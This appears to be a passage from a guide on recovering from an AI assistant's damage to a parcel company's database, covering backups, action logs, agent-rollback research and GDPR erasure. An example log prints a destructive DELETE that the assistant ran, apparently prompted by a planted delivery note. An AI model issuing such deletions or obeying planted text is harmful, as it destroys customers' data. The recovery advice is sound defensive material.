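PostgreSQL can also archive a log of every change, although this is off by default. With archiving on, Tern could restore the 02:00 backup and replay the changes up to the second before the deletion. This is called point-in-time restoration, and it would save all 600 shipments. If Tern copied the log to another location every five minutes and the whole server was destroyed, it would lose at most five minutes of work, or about four shipments.

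Restoration can also destroy later work. If a clerk discovers the mistake at 17:00, returning the live database to 14:00 would erase another 150 shipments. In eight small tests with text files, Waghmare and Sufi found that restoring a saved copy erased a later edit every time, whereas merging the versions preserved it. Tern should restore the old data into a separate database and copy back only the missing rows, first the shipments and then the events that refer to them.

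### What to record

To find the missing rows, Tern needs a log that connects each change to its cause:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-01T14:00:07Z",
  "user": "customer 17",
  "prompt": "You help customers of a parcel company. ...",
  "output": "DELETE FROM shipments WHERE status = 'delivered';",
  "action": "deleted shipments 1041, 1043, 1044, 1046"
}
```

Tern can use the recorded action to find which shipments to restore, and the output to see the missing condition. The full prompt would include any planted delivery note, and the recorded user shows whose session the application was acting in.

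Kaya and colleagues advise comparing the database before and after an agent runs, rather than relying on the agent's own account of the damage. In at least 20% of the 739 trials in which their agents caused damage, the agent left no usable description of it, mostly because it reached its turn limit before reporting.

After a leak, the log shows whose data got out and where it went. Tern can then warn those customers and replace any exposed credentials. The log itself contains personal data, so it needs restricted access and a deletion date. The assistant must not be able to alter it.

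### Systems that undo an agent's actions

*GoEX* (2024) proposed that people check a model's actions after they have run, with a way to undo them and limits on the damage. Later systems undo actions in different ways. SagaLLM, from 2025, prepares a compensating action for each step and runs these actions in reverse order if the task fails. STRATUS uses a separate agent to reverse actions from a stored list. *POLAR* (2026) objects that people can audit such a rollback only after it has run, so it looks for a recovery path before allowing the original action.

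*AgentRewind* (2026) restores an agent's files and its context together, while keeping information from the failed attempt. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) treats a whole task as one transaction, which commits only if the result meets the task's conditions.

These systems can restore only what they control. *Revisable by Design* (2026) points out that developers can always roll back an agent's context but only some of its effects on the outside world. They can't, for example, undo an email that has reached a stranger. *Always-On Agents* (2026) found some form of rollback in only 27 of the 435 works it surveyed, and undoing external effects was even rarer.

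Waghmare and Sufi classified 536 tools that agents can call through MCP. They rated 333 as changing nothing and 115 of the other 203 as irreversible. These ratings are provisional. When Sufi reviewed 148 of the tools with an AI's help, the new rating matched the original for only 75, and most of the others were rated harder to undo than before. A developer should therefore test the undo procedure for each tool before letting an agent act without approval.

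### The conflict with duties to erase personal data

Any method of keeping deleted rows can conflict with the law. Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) and its British counterpart, people can ask a company to erase their personal data. If customer 31 asks for this, filling in `deleted_at` only hides his address. *Ghost Vectors* (2026) examines this problem in databases that store text and images as lists of numbers for searching. Records could still be recovered from storage after soft deletion, so the paper argues that an empty search result does not prove the data was erased.

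A company may refuse a request to erase personal data if the law requires it to keep the data or if it needs the data for legal claims, according to *Right to erasure*, guidance from the ICO, the UK's data protection regulator. Tern might therefore be able to keep a proof of delivery for a time, but it would struggle to justify keeping a note about a faint doorbell.

Otherwise the company must respond without undue delay, and within a month at most. A 14-day delay fits within that limit, but Tern should still handle legal requests separately, by having an employee check the person's identity and then permanently delete the data. The assistant should pass such requests on, because the ICO says a valid request can be made to any part of an organisation and need not mention the law.

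Regulators differ on whether companies must delete personal data from backups. The ICO lets data remain in a backup until the company overwrites it, provided the company uses it for nothing else. The EDPB's *Implementation of the right to erasure by controllers* (2026), a report by the EU's data protection board, accepts that changing backups is not always advisable, and says companies should then record erasure requests and reapply them to any system they restore. According to ODO 24's *Data deletion from backups*, Poland's regulator stated in November 2025 that companies must delete the data from backups too.

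Under the more permissive approach, Tern could keep a list of the numbers of customers whose data it has erased. If it erased customer 31's data on December 1 and then, on December 3, restored a backup from November 30, his address would return. Tern would use the list to erase the address again before anyone used the restored data.

No retention period suits both purposes perfectly. Tern might not discover a missing proof of delivery for two months, but keeping every deleted address that long would be hard to justify. It could remove deleted data after 14 days, except for the few facts that prove delivery, which it could keep longer. To satisfy a stricter regulator, it could encrypt each customer's data with a separate key and destroy that key on request, which would make every backup copy unreadable. Losing a key by mistake would also make the data permanently unreadable, so the assistant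 must have no access to the keys.
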